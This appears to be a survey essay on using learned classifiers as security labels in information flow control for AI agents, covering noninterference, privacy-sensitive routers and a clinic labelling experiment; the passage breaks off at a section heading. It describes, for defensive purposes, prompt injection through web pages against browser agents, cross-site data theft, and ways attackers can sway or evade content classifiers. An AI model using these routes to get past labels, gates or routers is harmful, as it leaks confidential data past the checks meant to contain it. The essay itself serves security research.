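# Can learned classifiers serve as security labels in AI information flow control?

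## Security labels, noninterference and the two ways to label data

Information flow control is a branch of computer security that deals with where data goes after someone has read it. A system that uses it attaches a security label to each piece of data to record who may read the data or how restricted it is. The system carries the label through every copy and calculation and checks it before any data leaves. Computer scientists worked out the core theory in the 1970s and 1980s for operating systems and ordinary programs. In the last few years, researchers have applied it to AI agents, which are language models that read documents, call software tools and send messages on somebody's behalf.

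The theory takes the labels as given. In an office, somebody has to supply them, and many of the documents an assistant reads have no label or the wrong one. One shortcut is to have a trained model read each document and decide how sensitive it is. It is unclear how much of the theory's guarantee still holds when a model assigns the labels.

The more familiar way to protect a file is access control, which checks a reader's permission before opening the file. *Language-Based Information-Flow Security* (Sabelfeld and Myers, 2003) points out that this check restricts the release of information but not its later spread. An owner relying on access control alone would have to admit only programs that will never leak, and access control cannot identify those programs. An AI assistant is hard to trust in this way because it uses what it reads to write something new. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*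 (2026), a position paper from researchers at Google, NVIDIA and several US universities, makes the same distinction for agents. A sandbox controls whether the agent can access the data, while information flow control restricts what happens to the data afterwards.

### Labels, joins and gates

Suppose Ana runs a company that is secretly preparing to buy a competitor. Her AI assistant can open a merger memo, which only Ana and her finance chief Ben may read, and the office calendar, which is public. She asks the assistant to summarise the week ahead and email the summary to Dev, who looks after the building. The assistant reads both documents, writes a paragraph and calls its email tool. The email is a sink, a destination where data leaves the system's control. A web request is also a sink, as is a query to a cloud model run by another company.

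The simplest scheme has two labels, low for public data and high for confidential data. Offices need finer distinctions, and one common choice is the reader set, where a document's label is the set of people who may read it. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) uses reader sets in FIDES, an agent design from Microsoft. In Ana's case, the memo's label is {Ana, Ben} and the calendar's is the set of everyone.

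The summary draws on both documents, so its readers should be the people who may read both. Intersecting the two sets of readers gives {Ana, Ben}. Suppose the assistant had also opened a legal opinion that only Ana and the company's lawyer, Carla, may read. Intersecting {Ana, Ben} with {Ana, Carla} leaves {Ana}. Ben is excluded because the summary could contain information from the opinion, and Carla because it could contain information from the memo.

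This way of combining labels is a join, and it comes from Denning (1976), in *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow*. She starts with a set of security classes and a relation that says when information in class A may flow into class B, which later authors write as A ⊑ B. The classes form a lattice if the relation is a partial order and every pair of classes has a least upper bound and a greatest lower bound. The join A ⊔ B is the least upper bound, and two conditions define it:

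$$A \sqsubseteq A \sqcup B \quad\text{and}\quad B \sqsubseteq A \sqcup B$$

$$\text{if } A \sqsubseteq C \text{ and } B \sqsubseteq C, \text{ then } A \sqcup B \sqsubseteq C$$

The upper line makes the combined label at least as restrictive as each source's label, and the lower line makes it no more restrictive than that requires. With reader sets, fewer readers means more restrictive, so "everyone" is at the bottom of the lattice and the empty set, which means nobody may read the data, is at the top.

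Denning argued that these conditions follow from what information flow means. If a system allowed the assignment c := a + b but forbade c := a, a programmer could set b to zero and use the permitted assignment to copy a into c.

A policy gate is the ordinary code that compares a label with a destination. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, give the usual rule for sending, which is that a call may send data only if every recipient is one of that data's permitted readers. The assistant may therefore send its summary to Ben but not to Dev. The gate's decision depends only on the label and the recipients, so the wording of the email cannot change it.

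Dev's email stays blocked even if every sentence in it came from the calendar. Costa and colleagues label a model's output with the join of everything the model had in front of it, because they have no precise way to trace labels through a language model. Over a long session this gets expensive. *APPA* (2026), an agent system whose labels pair a reader set with a trust level, gives the arithmetic. If the session starts with readers R₀ and the i-th action brings in data with readers Aᵢ, then after n actions the permitted readers are

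$$R_0 \cap A_1 \cap A_2 \cap \dots \cap A_n$$

and an intersection can only shrink or stay the same. The name for this is label creep, the build-up of restrictive labels until the system may send almost nothing. Sabelfeld and Myers thought it made labelling at run time too restrictive to be generally useful. A good deal of the appeal of learned components comes from the hope of avoiding it.

### Noninterference

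Labels and gates are machinery. The property that they are supposed to secure has its own definition, from Goguen and Meseguer (1982), in *Security Policies and Security Models*. They model a computer as a machine that takes commands from users and shows each user some output. One group of users is noninterfering with another if nothing the first group does has any effect on what the second group can see. To make this exact, let w be any sequence of commands, let p_G(w) be the same sequence with every command from group G deleted, and let view_u(w) be what user u sees after w. Then G does not interfere with G′ when

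$$\text{for all } w \text{ and all } u \in G': \quad \mathrm{view}_u(w) = \mathrm{view}_u(p_G(w))$$

So the G′ users cannot tell whether the G users ever used the system. Goguen and Meseguer define a security policy as a set of such statements, separate from the description of the system. One can then try to prove that the system satisfies the policy.

For a program that takes inputs and produces outputs, the usual form is the one in Sabelfeld and Myers's survey, which traces the idea back to earlier work by Cohen. Take a deterministic program P with a low input ℓ and a secret input h, and write P_L for the part of its output that a low-clearance observer can see. P satisfies noninterference when

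$$\text{for all } \ell, h, h': \quad P_L(\ell, h) = P_L(\ell, h')$$

Equal low inputs give equal low outputs, whatever the secrets are. In Ana's office, with Dev as the observer, ℓ is the calendar and Ana's request, and h is the memo. If we replace the memo with one in which the deal has collapsed, or with a shopping list, Dev must get the same email as before, character for character, or no email both times.

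The definition compares two runs, so no single run can show that a program meets it. Dev's email could contain only public calendar entries and still violate noninterference if a different memo would have led the assistant to pick different entries. An auditor who searches the outbox for phrases from the memo would miss this violation, because that search detects only copied text.

Noninterference also covers all inputs. A thousand pairs of memos that produce identical emails do not establish it, because a single pair that produces two different emails would refute it. Proofs of noninterference therefore rely on the structure of the program, for instance by using a type checker that rejects any program with a path from secret data to public output. A classifier's accuracy is an average over a test set, not a guarantee for every input, and this difference matters a great deal when a classifier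 supplies the labels.

The guarantee covers only what the observer can see, so if Dev can notice that the assistant took longer than usual, P_L must include the time taken. Language models also usually sample their output at random, so the same input can give different text on different runs. The comparison therefore has to be between the probabilities of outputs. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) defines noninterference this way for programs that call language models.

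### Explicit and implicit flow

Denning distinguished two ways for a secret to get out. An explicit flow copies the secret, or something computed from it, to a destination:

```
summary = memo.text
send("dev", summary)
```

An implicit flow reveals the secret by which action the program takes:

```
if "merger" in memo.text:
    send("dev", "Please keep Friday free.")
```

The message in the second program is a fixed string containing nothing from the memo. But if Dev knows how the assistant behaves, he can infer from the message that a merger is under way, and from its absence that none is. Denning emphasized that the information flows whether or not the branch runs.

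Labels that a system attaches while a program runs are good at catching explicit flows. To catch implicit ones, the system can also add the label of a branch's condition to anything written inside that branch. This still misses some implicit flows, as Denning shows with a short program that she credits to Fenton. Let a be a secret that is either true or false.

```
b = c = False
if not a: c = True
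if not c: b = True
```

If a is true, the second line does nothing, and c stays false with a public label. The third line then sets b to true. Since the condition on that line depends only on c, which has a public label, b gets a public label too. If a is false, c becomes true and takes on a's secret label, the third line does nothing, and b stays false and public. In both cases b ends up equal to a, with a public label. The leak happens because c's label becomes secret only if the second line assigns to c. When a is true, that assignment is skipped, so c still has a public label when the third line uses it to set b.

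One repair is to raise the label on everything that the untaken branch could have written. That requires analyzing paths the program never took, which a compiler can do from source code. But an agent's branches are mostly choices made inside a language model, which have no source code to analyze. Costa and colleagues judged that full noninterference would amount to forbidding any publicly visible tool call after any tool call that might read a secret. They settled for a weaker property called explicit secrecy, which prevents direct copying but doesn't limit what an observer can infer from the choice and order of the agent's actions.

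### Declassification

Noninterference also forbids programs that people want. A login page that answers "wrong password" reveals something about the stored password, so one that satisfied noninterference would have to give the same reply to right and wrong passwords. In *A Model for Delimited Information Release*, Sabelfeld and Myers list password checking, information purchase and spreadsheet computation as programs that seem secure to most people but release part of a secret.

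Declassification is the deliberate, authorised lowering of a confidentiality label, or the release of labelled data. Ana needs it to get a room for Thursday's signing ceremony, because Dev books the rooms and the date is written only in the memo. She may decide that Dev can have the date but not the rest of the memo. An assistant that could never declassify anything would be safe, but of little use for work that involves a confidential document and an outside person on the same day.

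Goguen and Meseguer's formalism allows such exceptions. A policy can state that one group does not affect another except through a named set of commands, which opens one channel and keeps the guarantee for everything outside it. The formalism cannot determine which releases are right. At the sink, an authorised release looks the same as laundering, in which secret content loses its restrictive label because something rewrote, summarised or relabelled it. They differ in whether somebody with the authority to release the content decided to release it.

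Kolluri and colleagues considered letting their agent, Prudentia, ask its user to declassify data, but decided against it. They reasoned that whether a release is appropriate depends so much on the situation that it is better to ask the user to approve each blocked action than to lower a label for every use of the data. The user therefore has to make the judgement each time, and handing it to a model would save them many approvals.

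### Where labels come from

So far the memo has arrived already labeled {Ana, Ben}. If that label comes from the memo's origin, such as its owner, folder or access list, it is a provenance label. A content label is one that a classifier or language model infers by reading the data.

Provenance labels and content labels fail in different cases. Suppose Ben types "Signing with Northwind, 4 pm" into the public calendar. The entry is public by provenance, so a correct gate will send it to anybody, though a model that reads the entry might flag it. Provenance labels can also be too strict. If page nine of the memo lists the canteen's opening hours, a provenance label restricts them along with the rest of the memo. Content labels seem to do better in both cases, but they depend on the words, so whoever writes the words has some influence over the label. A model may also label the same document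 differently on different occasions.

A deeper difficulty is that a document's text may not contain everything its label has to record. *Privacy Conductor* (Thornton, Pritom and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that illustrates this. It puts a fixed gate between an assistant and an organisation's document store. The gate decides from the document's label and facts about the requester, never from the document's text, and refuses whatever it cannot positively permit. It uses two fields of the label, a sensitivity tier (such as "public" or "financial") and a list of the roles that may receive the document. The tier is descriptive, and the document is evidence for it, but the list is normative because it records what some authority has decided. A careful reader of the merger memo could work out that it is highly confidential, but the text need not indicate that Ben is allowed to see it and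 Carla is not.

The formal guarantee depends on the labels, however the system obtains them. Kolluri and colleagues state that their protection holds when the data has appropriate labels and the policies are correct. In the formula above, noninterference protects h, but a memo that somebody has marked public is part of ℓ, so it is not protected, whatever it contains.

### Three jobs for a model

A learned component can be used at three points in this system. It can assign the first label by reading the memo and marking it confidential. It can decide which labels pass to derived text, for example by judging that the summary drew only on the calendar and so need not inherit the memo's restrictions on readers. Or it can approve a release by reading the blocked email to Dev and deciding that the signing date may be sent.

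*GIF* (2026) describes a system with a separate component for each job. One labels individual tokens (the word fragments that a language model processes), another estimates how much information flows from one labelled token to another, and a declassifier makes the final security decision. In its tests, a language model makes that decision by returning "allow" or "deny". *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow* (2026) takes its labels from provenance. It marks the user's sensitive records and treats whatever the agent derives from them as restricted. It blocks all writes to untrusted recipients, regardless of content, and uses an isolated checker to examine the content only when the recipient is unknown.

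All three jobs require trusting the model. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* treats the model as an untrusted component. It counts the labels, and the code that propagates and enforces them, as part of the trusted computing base, the set of components that must work correctly for the system to be secure. Thornton and colleagues note that the same language model can be untrusted when it answers questions as the assistant and trusted when it labels the documents.

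The damage from a mistake depends on which job the model is doing. If it marks the memo public, every later join uses the wrong label, so every summary, reply and search result that draws on the memo inherits the mistake. If it wrongly drops the memo's label from one summary, the memo is still protected, but that summary can be sent anywhere. If it wrongly approves one email, that email leaves the system, but the labels on everything still inside remain correct.

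## Routers that judge sensitivity and choose where data goes

Many organisations run small language models on their own machines and rent larger ones from a cloud provider. A program called a router receives each request and picks the model to answer it. Most routers choose based on cost and difficulty. Some also judge whether a request contains anything sensitive, and send it to a local model if it does. In information flow control terms, the cloud model is a sink, the judgement is a content label, and the rule that turns the label into a destination is the policy gate.

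Suppose Ana's company installs such a router, and she pastes part of the merger memo into the assistant to have it shortened. The memo's label, {Ana, Ben}, is not copied with the text, so the router can judge sensitivity only from the words.

### What the code enforces and what it assumes

*ComplianceGate* (2026) describes a router for regulated firms, which often have to keep personal data inside one country. An encoder, a small model that classifies text, reads the first 128 tokens of each query and picks one of six labels, which cover the query's difficulty and whether it contains personal data. The router sends queries with personal data to a local endpoint and the others to a small, medium or large model, depending on difficulty. It also uses the local endpoint when the encoder's confidence is below 80%. Classification takes 7 milliseconds and happens before any language model receives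 the query.

The paper reports 99.2% accuracy for the encoder. It also claims that the design makes residency violations, in which personal data leaves its permitted territory, "structurally impossible". To test that claim, let S be the set of queries that contain personal data, F the set that the encoder flags or is unsure about, and L the set that the router keeps local. The claim is that S lies inside L, and it needs two premises:

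$$S \subseteq F \quad\text{and}\quad F \subseteq L \quad\Rightarrow\quad S \subseteq L$$

The premise F ⊆ L depends on ordinary code, so a reviewer can read the routing rule and check that no flagged query takes another path. The premise S ⊆ F depends on how a trained model behaves on every query it will ever receive, and nothing in the architecture makes it true. *ComplianceGate* notes that a query could violate residency if the encoder misses the personal data in it. The architecture therefore rules out violations only for flagged queries, and it would do the same if the router flagged queries at random. Even a perfect encoder would not achieve noninterference, because a routing decision that depends on sensitivity also reveals information about sensitivity, as *Sensitive-Topic Leakage Through LLM Routing Metadata* (2026) points out.

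Putting the judge in front of the models keeps flagged queries off the remote machine, so nobody has to trust the provider to delete them. The 80% rule also helps, but only when the encoder's confidence is low. It doesn't catch confident mistakes, and the 128-token limit makes those easy to construct. If Ana pastes in the whole memo and it opens with a page of boilerplate, the encoder may assign a label with 99% confidence without processing the sensitive part.

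The paper's main experiment measured speed and cost and did not test the privacy claim. Over 600 queries, it found a 39% lower median response time and cost savings of 33% to 52%. All the queries ran in one cloud region, so none could have crossed a border. They were also short, averaging about 14 tokens in the simple group and 33 in the complex one, so the 128-token limit hardly mattered. Even if the experiment had tested privacy, 600 queries would be too few to rule out a rare miss. The 99.2% figure comes from a separate test set that the paper does not describe. It is also an average over six labels, so it reflects errors that waste money without exposing data, such as mistaking a simple query for a medium one.

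In *LLM-Redactor*, Agyemang, Kponyo and colleagues (2026) measured how much sensitive data leaks through such a gate. They wrote 1,300 artificial prompts and marked 4,014 sensitive items in them. In one set-up, a small local model answered the requests it judged trivial, and everything else went to the cloud unchanged. Prompts answered locally leaked nothing, but routing gave no protection to those sent to the cloud. Across all prompts, 6.3% of the sensitive items leaked from prose full of personal details, 24.2% from configuration files containing passwords and keys, and 59.9% from proprietary code. Much of the difference came from how often the router chose the local model, which was 94% of the time for the personal prose and 38% for the code. This router judged difficulty, so the figures are not miss rates for a sensitivity classifier.

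### Looking for names and numbers

*vLLM Semantic Router* (Liu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes an open-source router whose classifier labels individual stretches of text, which gives an administrator more to base rules on than a single label for the whole query. For each stretch, the classifier outputs the start and end positions, a type such as "person" or "credit card", and a confidence c. The administrator sets a threshold θ and a list of allowed types, and the rule fires if any detection has c ≥ θ and a type that is not on the list. The administrator can then have the router refuse the request without contacting any model, or restrict the choice to models on the organisation's own premises. Red Hat's *Intelligent inference request routing for large language models* (2025) recommends the second option for organisations that use both internal and public models, though in its worked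 example, a request containing a customer's credit card number is refused.

The classifier can only detect a fixed set of types of personally identifiable information (PII). vLLM Semantic Router's *PII Detection* (version 0.1) lists sixteen, including names, phone numbers, dates and organisations, but none for trade secrets or planned mergers. Suppose Ana writes "We sign with Northwind on Thursday". The classifier could find an organisation and a date, but the project's sample settings allow both types, along with one other, for technical work because they are so common in code and configuration files. With those settings, the router sends Ana's sentence to the cloud. If she blocks both types, the router will stop her from asking a cloud model about any company or day of the week.

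The threshold is easy to set in the wrong direction. A later edition of vLLM Semantic Router's *PII Detection* recommends 0.9 to 0.95 for healthcare, finance and law, which it describes as strict detection, and 0.5 to 0.65 for code and testing tools. But a higher threshold produces fewer detections. If the classifier is 85% confident that a word is a patient's name, the rule fires in the testing tool but not in the hospital. The higher setting does reduce false alarms, which the documentation gives as a reason for it, but it also causes more misses where a miss does the most harm. The router also treats a detection below the threshold as no detection, whereas *ComplianceGate* sends doubtful cases to the local endpoint.

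Zhan, Shen and colleagues (2025), in *PRISM*, combine entity detection with a third option between local and cloud. The user's device first runs a named-entity recogniser, a program that finds names, places and similar items. Each category of entity has a fixed sensitivity weight between 0 and 1, and the risk score of a prompt P is the sum of the weights of the m entities found in it:

$$R(P) = \sum_{i=1}^{m} w_{c_i}$$

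The device then marks every entity as needing protection if the prompt contains a first-person pronoun or a person's name, and marks none otherwise. So it marks Tokyo in "I plan to travel solo to Tokyo for three days" but not in "Which country is Tokyo located in?" This shortcut is reasonable for private individuals but works badly for business secrets. "Northwind's board will accept the offer on Thursday" contains no first-person pronoun or person's name, so the device would mark nothing.

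A small trained function receives the risk score and the marks, but not the prompt's words, and assigns a probability to each of three routes: answering locally, sending the prompt to the cloud unchanged, or collaborating with the cloud model. The device takes the most probable route. On the collaborative route, it replaces marked entities at random before sending the prompt, so "travel solo to Tokyo" might arrive as "travel solo to Emma". The cloud model writes a short outline for a generic trip, and the local model, which still has the original prompt, turns the outline into an answer about Tokyo.

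The random replacement comes with a theorem. For an item with K possible values and a privacy budget ε, the device keeps the true value with probability

$$p = \frac{e^{\varepsilon}}{e^{\varepsilon} + K - 1}$$

and otherwise picks one of the others at random. This satisfies local differential privacy, which means that no output is more than e^ε times as likely under one true value as under another. PRISM does it twice, first for the entity's category and then for its value, and the two budgets add up. In the main experiments they were 0.3 and 0.7. With ten categories, the true one would survive about 13% of the time.

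Zhan and colleagues also propose giving the category a larger share of the budget when an entity is very sensitive, to hide the category better. But in their formula a larger budget means less noise, so the rule would expose the category more and add more noise to the value, though the bound on the total still holds.

That bound covers each entity the device has marked and sent along the collaborative route. It does not cover entities the recogniser missed, the rest of the sentence, or anything on the direct cloud route. Zhan and colleagues illustrate this gap when they argue that masking names is not enough. One record describes a masked person who owns a black dog and walks after dinner, and another contains a complaint that the owner of the black dog throws out rubbish on Tuesdays. The dog links the two records, but "black dog" is not a named entity, so PRISM's noise would normally leave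 it in place too.

PRISM was tested on 160 prompts for answer quality, energy use and time. It took 7.9 seconds, compared with 17.8 for answering everything locally, and gave better answers. The reported results don't include how many prompts PRISM routed wrongly, which a confidentiality claim would need.

### Rewriting the request first

When a user pastes in an entire document, a cloud model usually needs only a small part of it. *Privacy Guard & Token Parsimony by Prompt and Context Handling* (Langiu, 2026) proposes a local language model that reads the whole conversation, splits the request into smaller tasks and rewrites each with as little context as possible. The local model then picks one of four destinations for each task. From least to most trusted, these are free public services, standard commercial services, models hosted in a required jurisdiction and the institution's own hardware.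 If the local model detects a risk that it cannot remove by rewriting, it blocks the task or sends it to one of the more trusted destinations.

Langiu claims "Zero Leakage" for this design and supports this with a theorem that shortening a prompt necessarily removes secrets from it. The proof sketch assumes that a summariser drops sensitive details because the task does not need them. Langiu's own results contradict this assumption. In a first run of 40 prompts, a 7-billion-parameter model let at least one secret through every time, even though it cut the long pasted documents by more than half. In a run of 1,000 prompts, 420 of 3,250 secrets (12.9%) leaked. All 420 were institutional secrets, such as cryptographic keys and network addresses, in long server logs. The model removed every personal secret and every secret in a short, well-structured prompt.

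Larger models did not always leak less. On 50 of the hardest logs, a 30-billion-parameter model leaked 54.4% of the secrets. A 70-billion-parameter model leaked 1.2% (3 of 250). Langiu concludes that the system needs a deterministic filter, such as a pattern matcher, in front of the model. A pattern matcher would suit keys and network addresses, which have a fixed format, but would not recognise Ana's merger. Agyemang and colleagues found that pattern matching alone caught every email address and cloud access key in their prompts but missed all the names of people and organisations.

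Langiu's leak test counted any secret in the outgoing text as a leak, regardless of where the text was sent. It therefore measured how well the rewriting removed secrets. How often the guard picks the right destination remains untested.

### A gate that does not read the page

The routers above all classify a text by reading it, so its author can influence the result. Google took a different approach for the AI agent in its Chrome browser, which clicks and types on websites for the user. The main danger is prompt injection, where somebody hides instructions in a web page for the agent to follow. *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025) describes a gating function that decides which origins (roughly, websites) are relevant to the user's current task. The agent can only read from some of these origins, but can both read from and act on others. The browser can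 enforce part of this by never showing the model content from other origins.

The gating function receives no untrusted web content, and a related component that approves or rejects each action the agent proposes receives only metadata about the action. A hostile page therefore cannot influence either of them directly. It can still influence them indirectly, because the model that proposes websites and actions reads pages, and a page might lead it to propose something that looks relevant. The University of Washington's *Agentic Browsers and the Same-Origin Policy* found that, once a prompt injection succeeds, the preconditions for stealing data across websites exist in Chrome with Gemini and several rival products.

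Chrome's gate checks whether a website is relevant to the task but doesn't assess how sensitive the data is. If Ana asks the agent to email a summary, both her document store and her webmail are relevant, so text from the first may flow into the second. The two sets don't distinguish an email to Ben from an email to Dev. Chrome leaves that to a separate step, in which the agent "will try to pause" and ask the user before sending a message. The first version also simplified the full design by tracking only the websites that the agent may both read and act on.

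A web address that the model writes itself can carry a secret in its text, so Google used a deterministic check, rather than a model's judgement, to restrict the agent to known, public addresses. Parker claims only that the whole arrangement limits where data can go, not that it makes leaks impossible.

### What a single query leaves out

Suppose the router correctly keeps Ana's first request, which includes the memo, on the local model. She then types "Make it shorter". That message contains nothing sensitive, so a router that judges only the latest message can send the request to the cloud. But as Liu and colleagues note, chat requests in the common OpenAI format include the full conversation history, so the memo is sent too. vLLM Semantic Router has a setting that scans earlier messages. According to its documentation, the setting is off by default, but turning it on is advised for conversations.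 The example on a newer page, *PII Signal*, has it on.

Joins would solve this problem but cause label creep. Once the memo is in the conversation, every later request that includes it inherits its label and stays local. A router that rescans the whole history avoids the creep, but it has to find the memo again on every turn, and one miss is enough to send the memo out. The scans also get longer as the conversation grows, and Langiu's guard did worst on long inputs.

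Harmless facts can also become sensitive when combined. *Data-Sensitivity-Tier Model Routing* (2026), an engineer's guide on tianpan.co, gives the example of a name, which is internal information on its own but needs the protection of a health record when paired with a diagnosis. The join of two internal labels is still internal, so somebody has to write an extra rule for the combination. A model that reads both facts together could in principle do better, but the evidence so far is discouraging. Agyemang and colleagues included 200 prompts that identify somebody without a name, such as a finance chief "whose wife works at the competitor". When they combined local routing, redaction and rephrasing, at least part of the identifying phrase still reached the cloud in 43.6% of cases. Their test counts any shared run of four characters as a leak, so it overstates how often a reader could identify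 the person.

The third omission is what happens to flagged queries when the local model is down. It undermines the premise F ⊆ L, which looked safe because it concerned only code. Many systems switch automatically to a backup, but according to tianpan.co, switching sensitive data to an endpoint without the right legal cover is a violation, not merely a drop in service. Liu and colleagues leave this switching to a separate infrastructure layer, so a routing rule can name a model without specifying where it runs. If an administrator registers a cloud copy as the backup for a local model, the privacy rule could pick the right model and the request could still go to the cloud. To prevent that, the backup system has to check the label too. *ComplianceGate* states that its fallback remains compliant but gives no mechanism.

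Some of these judgements are unnecessary because the data already has a label. When a database column is tagged as personal data, tianpan.co advises passing that tag from the catalogue to the router. Ana's memo had a provenance label before she copied from it, and a router that received this label would not have needed to estimate the text's sensitivity.

| Scheme | Input to the judgement | Granularity | Destinations | Action when unsure | Guarantee claimed |
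|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| *ComplianceGate* | First 128 tokens of the query | One label per query | Local endpoint, or a model sized to the query | Local endpoint if confidence is below 80% | Residency violations "structurally impossible" |
| vLLM Semantic Router (Liu and colleagues) | Latest message by default, optionally the whole history | Stretches of text, then one decision per request | Refusal, on-premise models or any model | Ignores detections below the threshold | No formal guarantee |
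| PRISM (Zhan and colleagues) | Entities found in the prompt, plus first-person words | Entities, then one route per prompt | Local model, cloud model, or cloud model with noise added | Takes the most probable route | Local differential privacy for each marked entity on the collaborative route |
| Privacy Guard (Langiu) | Whole conversation | One decision per sub-task | Four levels, from free public services to own hardware | No rule for doubtful cases; blocks or reroutes risks it detects | "Zero Leakage" |
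| Chrome's gating function (Parker) | Proposed websites and the user's task, without untrusted web content | One decision per website | Read only, read and act, or no access | No rule for doubtful cases; after repeated rejections the user can take over | Limits on leaks between websites, with no formal guarantee |

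## How accurately models assign sensitivity labels and recipient lists

A router only has to classify requests as sensitive or not, but a gate in front of a shared document store also needs a list of who may read each document. Thornton and colleagues tested how well a model can supply both the sensitivity labels and the recipient lists. They had a model instead of a person write the labels for Privacy Conductor, their fixed gate between an assistant and an organisation's documents, and left everything else unchanged.

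### A clinic with 105 documents

The experiment uses an invented medical clinic with 105 documents of 21 types, such as lab reports, insurance claims and employment contracts. The 24 people who can request them are ten patients, four doctors, four nurses, and two people each from billing, HR and IT. If everyone requests every document, the gate makes 24 × 105 = 2,520 decisions.

Each document has one of seven sensitivity tiers and a list of the roles that may receive it. The gate checks that the requester's role is on the list. If the tier covers information about individuals, it also checks that the clinic has assigned the requester to the person concerned. A nurse can therefore open a lab report only if the list includes nurses and the patient is assigned to her. With hand-written labels, the gate permitted 259 requests and refused 2,261, and every decision matched the intended policy.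 Any mistake the gate makes with model-assigned labels must therefore come from a label.

The labelling model received each document's title, type, subject and full text. Its instructions defined the tiers and roles and gave general rules, for example that mental-health records go only to doctors. The researchers tested six models, one of them both with and without extended thinking, in which a model reasons at length before it answers. Each of the seven configurations labelled all the documents five times. The last column of the table counts the decisions that differed between the five passes, and the other columns describe the first pass.

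| Configuration | Tier correct | Role list correct | Wrongly released | Wrongly refused | Changed between passes |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8 | 78% | 55% | 40 | 31 | 115 |
| Opus 4.8, no extended thinking | 83% | 57% | 44 | 27 | 108 |
| Sonnet 5 | 82% | 52% | 64 | 34 | 96 |
| Haiku 4.5 | 84% | 30% | 39 | 28 | 124 |
| GPT-5.4 | 86% | 23% | 9 | 100 | 40 |
| GPT-5.4-mini | 83% | 80% | 11 | 26 | 28 |
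| GPT-5.4-nano | 82% | 69% | 16 | 36 | 13 |

The gate permits between 0.4% and 2.8% of the requests it should refuse, and refuses between 10% and 39% of those it should permit.

To find the cause of each wrong release, the researchers restored one field of the label at a time to its hand-written value and ran the gate again. The role list was the cause every time, partly because the gate uses the tier only to decide whether the requester needs an assignment, and five of the seven tiers require one. Most tier mistakes involved records with both clinical and financial content, and confusing those two tiers does not change the gate's decision. The same mistakes would matter in a system that sent clinical and financial records to different places.

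The tier scores are also less impressive than they look. Nineteen of the 21 document types occur at only one tier, and the models had access to each document's type. A table listing the most common tier for each type would have been right on 100 of the 105 documents, more than any of the models.

The researchers counted a role list as correct only if it matched exactly. Each list involves six yes-or-no decisions, one per role, so a model that got each decision right 95% of the time, independently, would get the whole list right only 0.95⁶ ≈ 74% of the time. These compounding errors explain part of the gap between the two fields.

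An incorrect recipient list doesn't always cause a wrong release. GPT-5.4 got the fewest lists right but also wrongly released the fewest documents. A wrongly added role has no effect unless somebody in that role also has an assignment to the patient, and people, not models, wrote the assignments. Anthropic's models wrongly added roles two to four and a half times as often as they wrongly omitted them, while for OpenAI's models the ratio was between 0.7 and 1.4. The choice of labelling model therefore affects how permissive the policy is.

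The researchers assumed that everyone acts in good faith, so the results don't show what happens when someone words a document to get a particular label.

### The same documents, labelled again

None of the seven configurations gave the same labels on all five passes. Depending on the configuration, the tier was consistent across passes for 87% to 99% of documents, but the role list for only 26% to 91%. OpenAI's models ran at temperature 0, which removes deliberate randomness, where the service allowed it, but their labels still changed. Anthropic's models ran at their default settings, which may include random sampling, so the two families are not directly comparable.

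For Opus 4.8, the number of wrong releases ranged from 34 to 57 across passes. A clinic that labels its documents once gets one of these policies by chance. If it relabels them at every request, a nurse who is refused a record in the morning may receive it in the afternoon.

The number of changed decisions is a poor measure of the danger. GPT-5.4 changed 40 decisions, but none involved a document whose release the policy forbids. GPT-5.4-nano changed only 13, but nine of them did.

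Taking a majority vote over the five passes did not reliably help. It gave 33 wrong releases for Opus 4.8, barely below its best single pass. For Sonnet 5 it gave 66, which was worse than any single pass. Voting removes mistakes that a model makes occasionally but reinforces those it makes more often than not. Suppose a model wrongly adds nurses to a certain list with probability p on each pass, independently. The majority of five passes is then wrong with probability

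$$\sum_{k=3}^{5} \binom{5}{k} p^k (1-p)^{5-k}$$

If p is 20%, voting lowers the error rate to about 6%. If p is 60%, voting raises it to 68%.

Larger models were not consistently better. GPT-5.4 got far fewer lists right than its two smaller versions. More reasoning did not clearly help either. Opus 4.8 averaged 34 wrong releases per pass without extended thinking and 45 with it. But among requests that the policy refuses, it gave inconsistent answers on 73 without extended thinking and 66 with it.

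Replacing the labelling model can also change many labels. *Understanding Annotator Safety Policy with Interpretability* (2026) compared different models' labels for a set of chatbot safety examples. Pairs of models gave different labels to 10% to 20% of the examples, even when both models came from the same family.

### What a recipient list depends on

Thornton and colleagues attribute the gap to the fact that the tier describes the document, while the list records somebody's decision about who receives it. A model that reads Ana's merger memo can only guess who is on the list. Companies usually involve their lawyers in a merger, so a sensible guess would be Ana, Ben and Carla, but Ana has so far told only Ben. If she brings Carla in on Monday, the correct list will change and the memo's text will not. A labeller that reads only the text, and always gives the same text the same list, must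 therefore be wrong either before or after the change.

This puts a ceiling on accuracy. Let X be a document's text, Y its correct list, and f any rule for guessing the list from the text. Then

$$\max_f \Pr[f(X) = Y] = \mathbb{E}\left[\max_y \Pr(Y = y \mid X)\right]$$

The best rule picks, for each text, the list that most often goes with it. If the most common list for memos like Ana's is correct 70% of the time, no rule can exceed 70% accuracy on those memos. A larger model or more votes cannot raise this limit, which also applies to a human who has only the text. Ana can do better because she made the decision. A model could also do better if it received the memo's sharing history, but its label would then be partly a provenance label.

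The clinic experiment only partly supports this explanation. GPT-5.4-mini got 80% of the lists right, so most of them were predictable from the documents and instructions. The other models may often have made mistakes because they didn't know the clinic's conventions, which somebody could have written down. The instructions were also somewhat ambiguous, since they asked for both all the roles that legitimately apply and the minimum necessary. Rerunning the experiment with a complete written policy would show how many of the mistakes remain.

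With such a policy, a model might only need to report facts, and ordinary code could work out the recipient list. This is probably the most promising use of a model as a labeller, but *Judging facts, judging norms* (Balagopalan, Madras and colleagues, 2023) found a problem with separating factual questions from the rule. The researchers wrote simple rules for office clothing, school meals, dogs in apartment buildings and online comments. One group of people saw the rule and judged whether each item broke it. Another group only answered factual questions, such as whether a dog was large, and the researchers applied the rule to their answers.

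Cases were judged violations more often when a rule was applied to people's factual answers than when people judged each case directly. The average difference was under 8 percentage points for clothing and comments, and between 15 and 20 points for meals and dogs. The difference remained when the people giving factual answers were told what the facts were for. Models trained on the factual answers also found more violations than human judges did. If the same holds for confidential documents, a system that extracts facts and applies a rule will block more than people who judge each case directly would.

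### Disclosures that courts had judged

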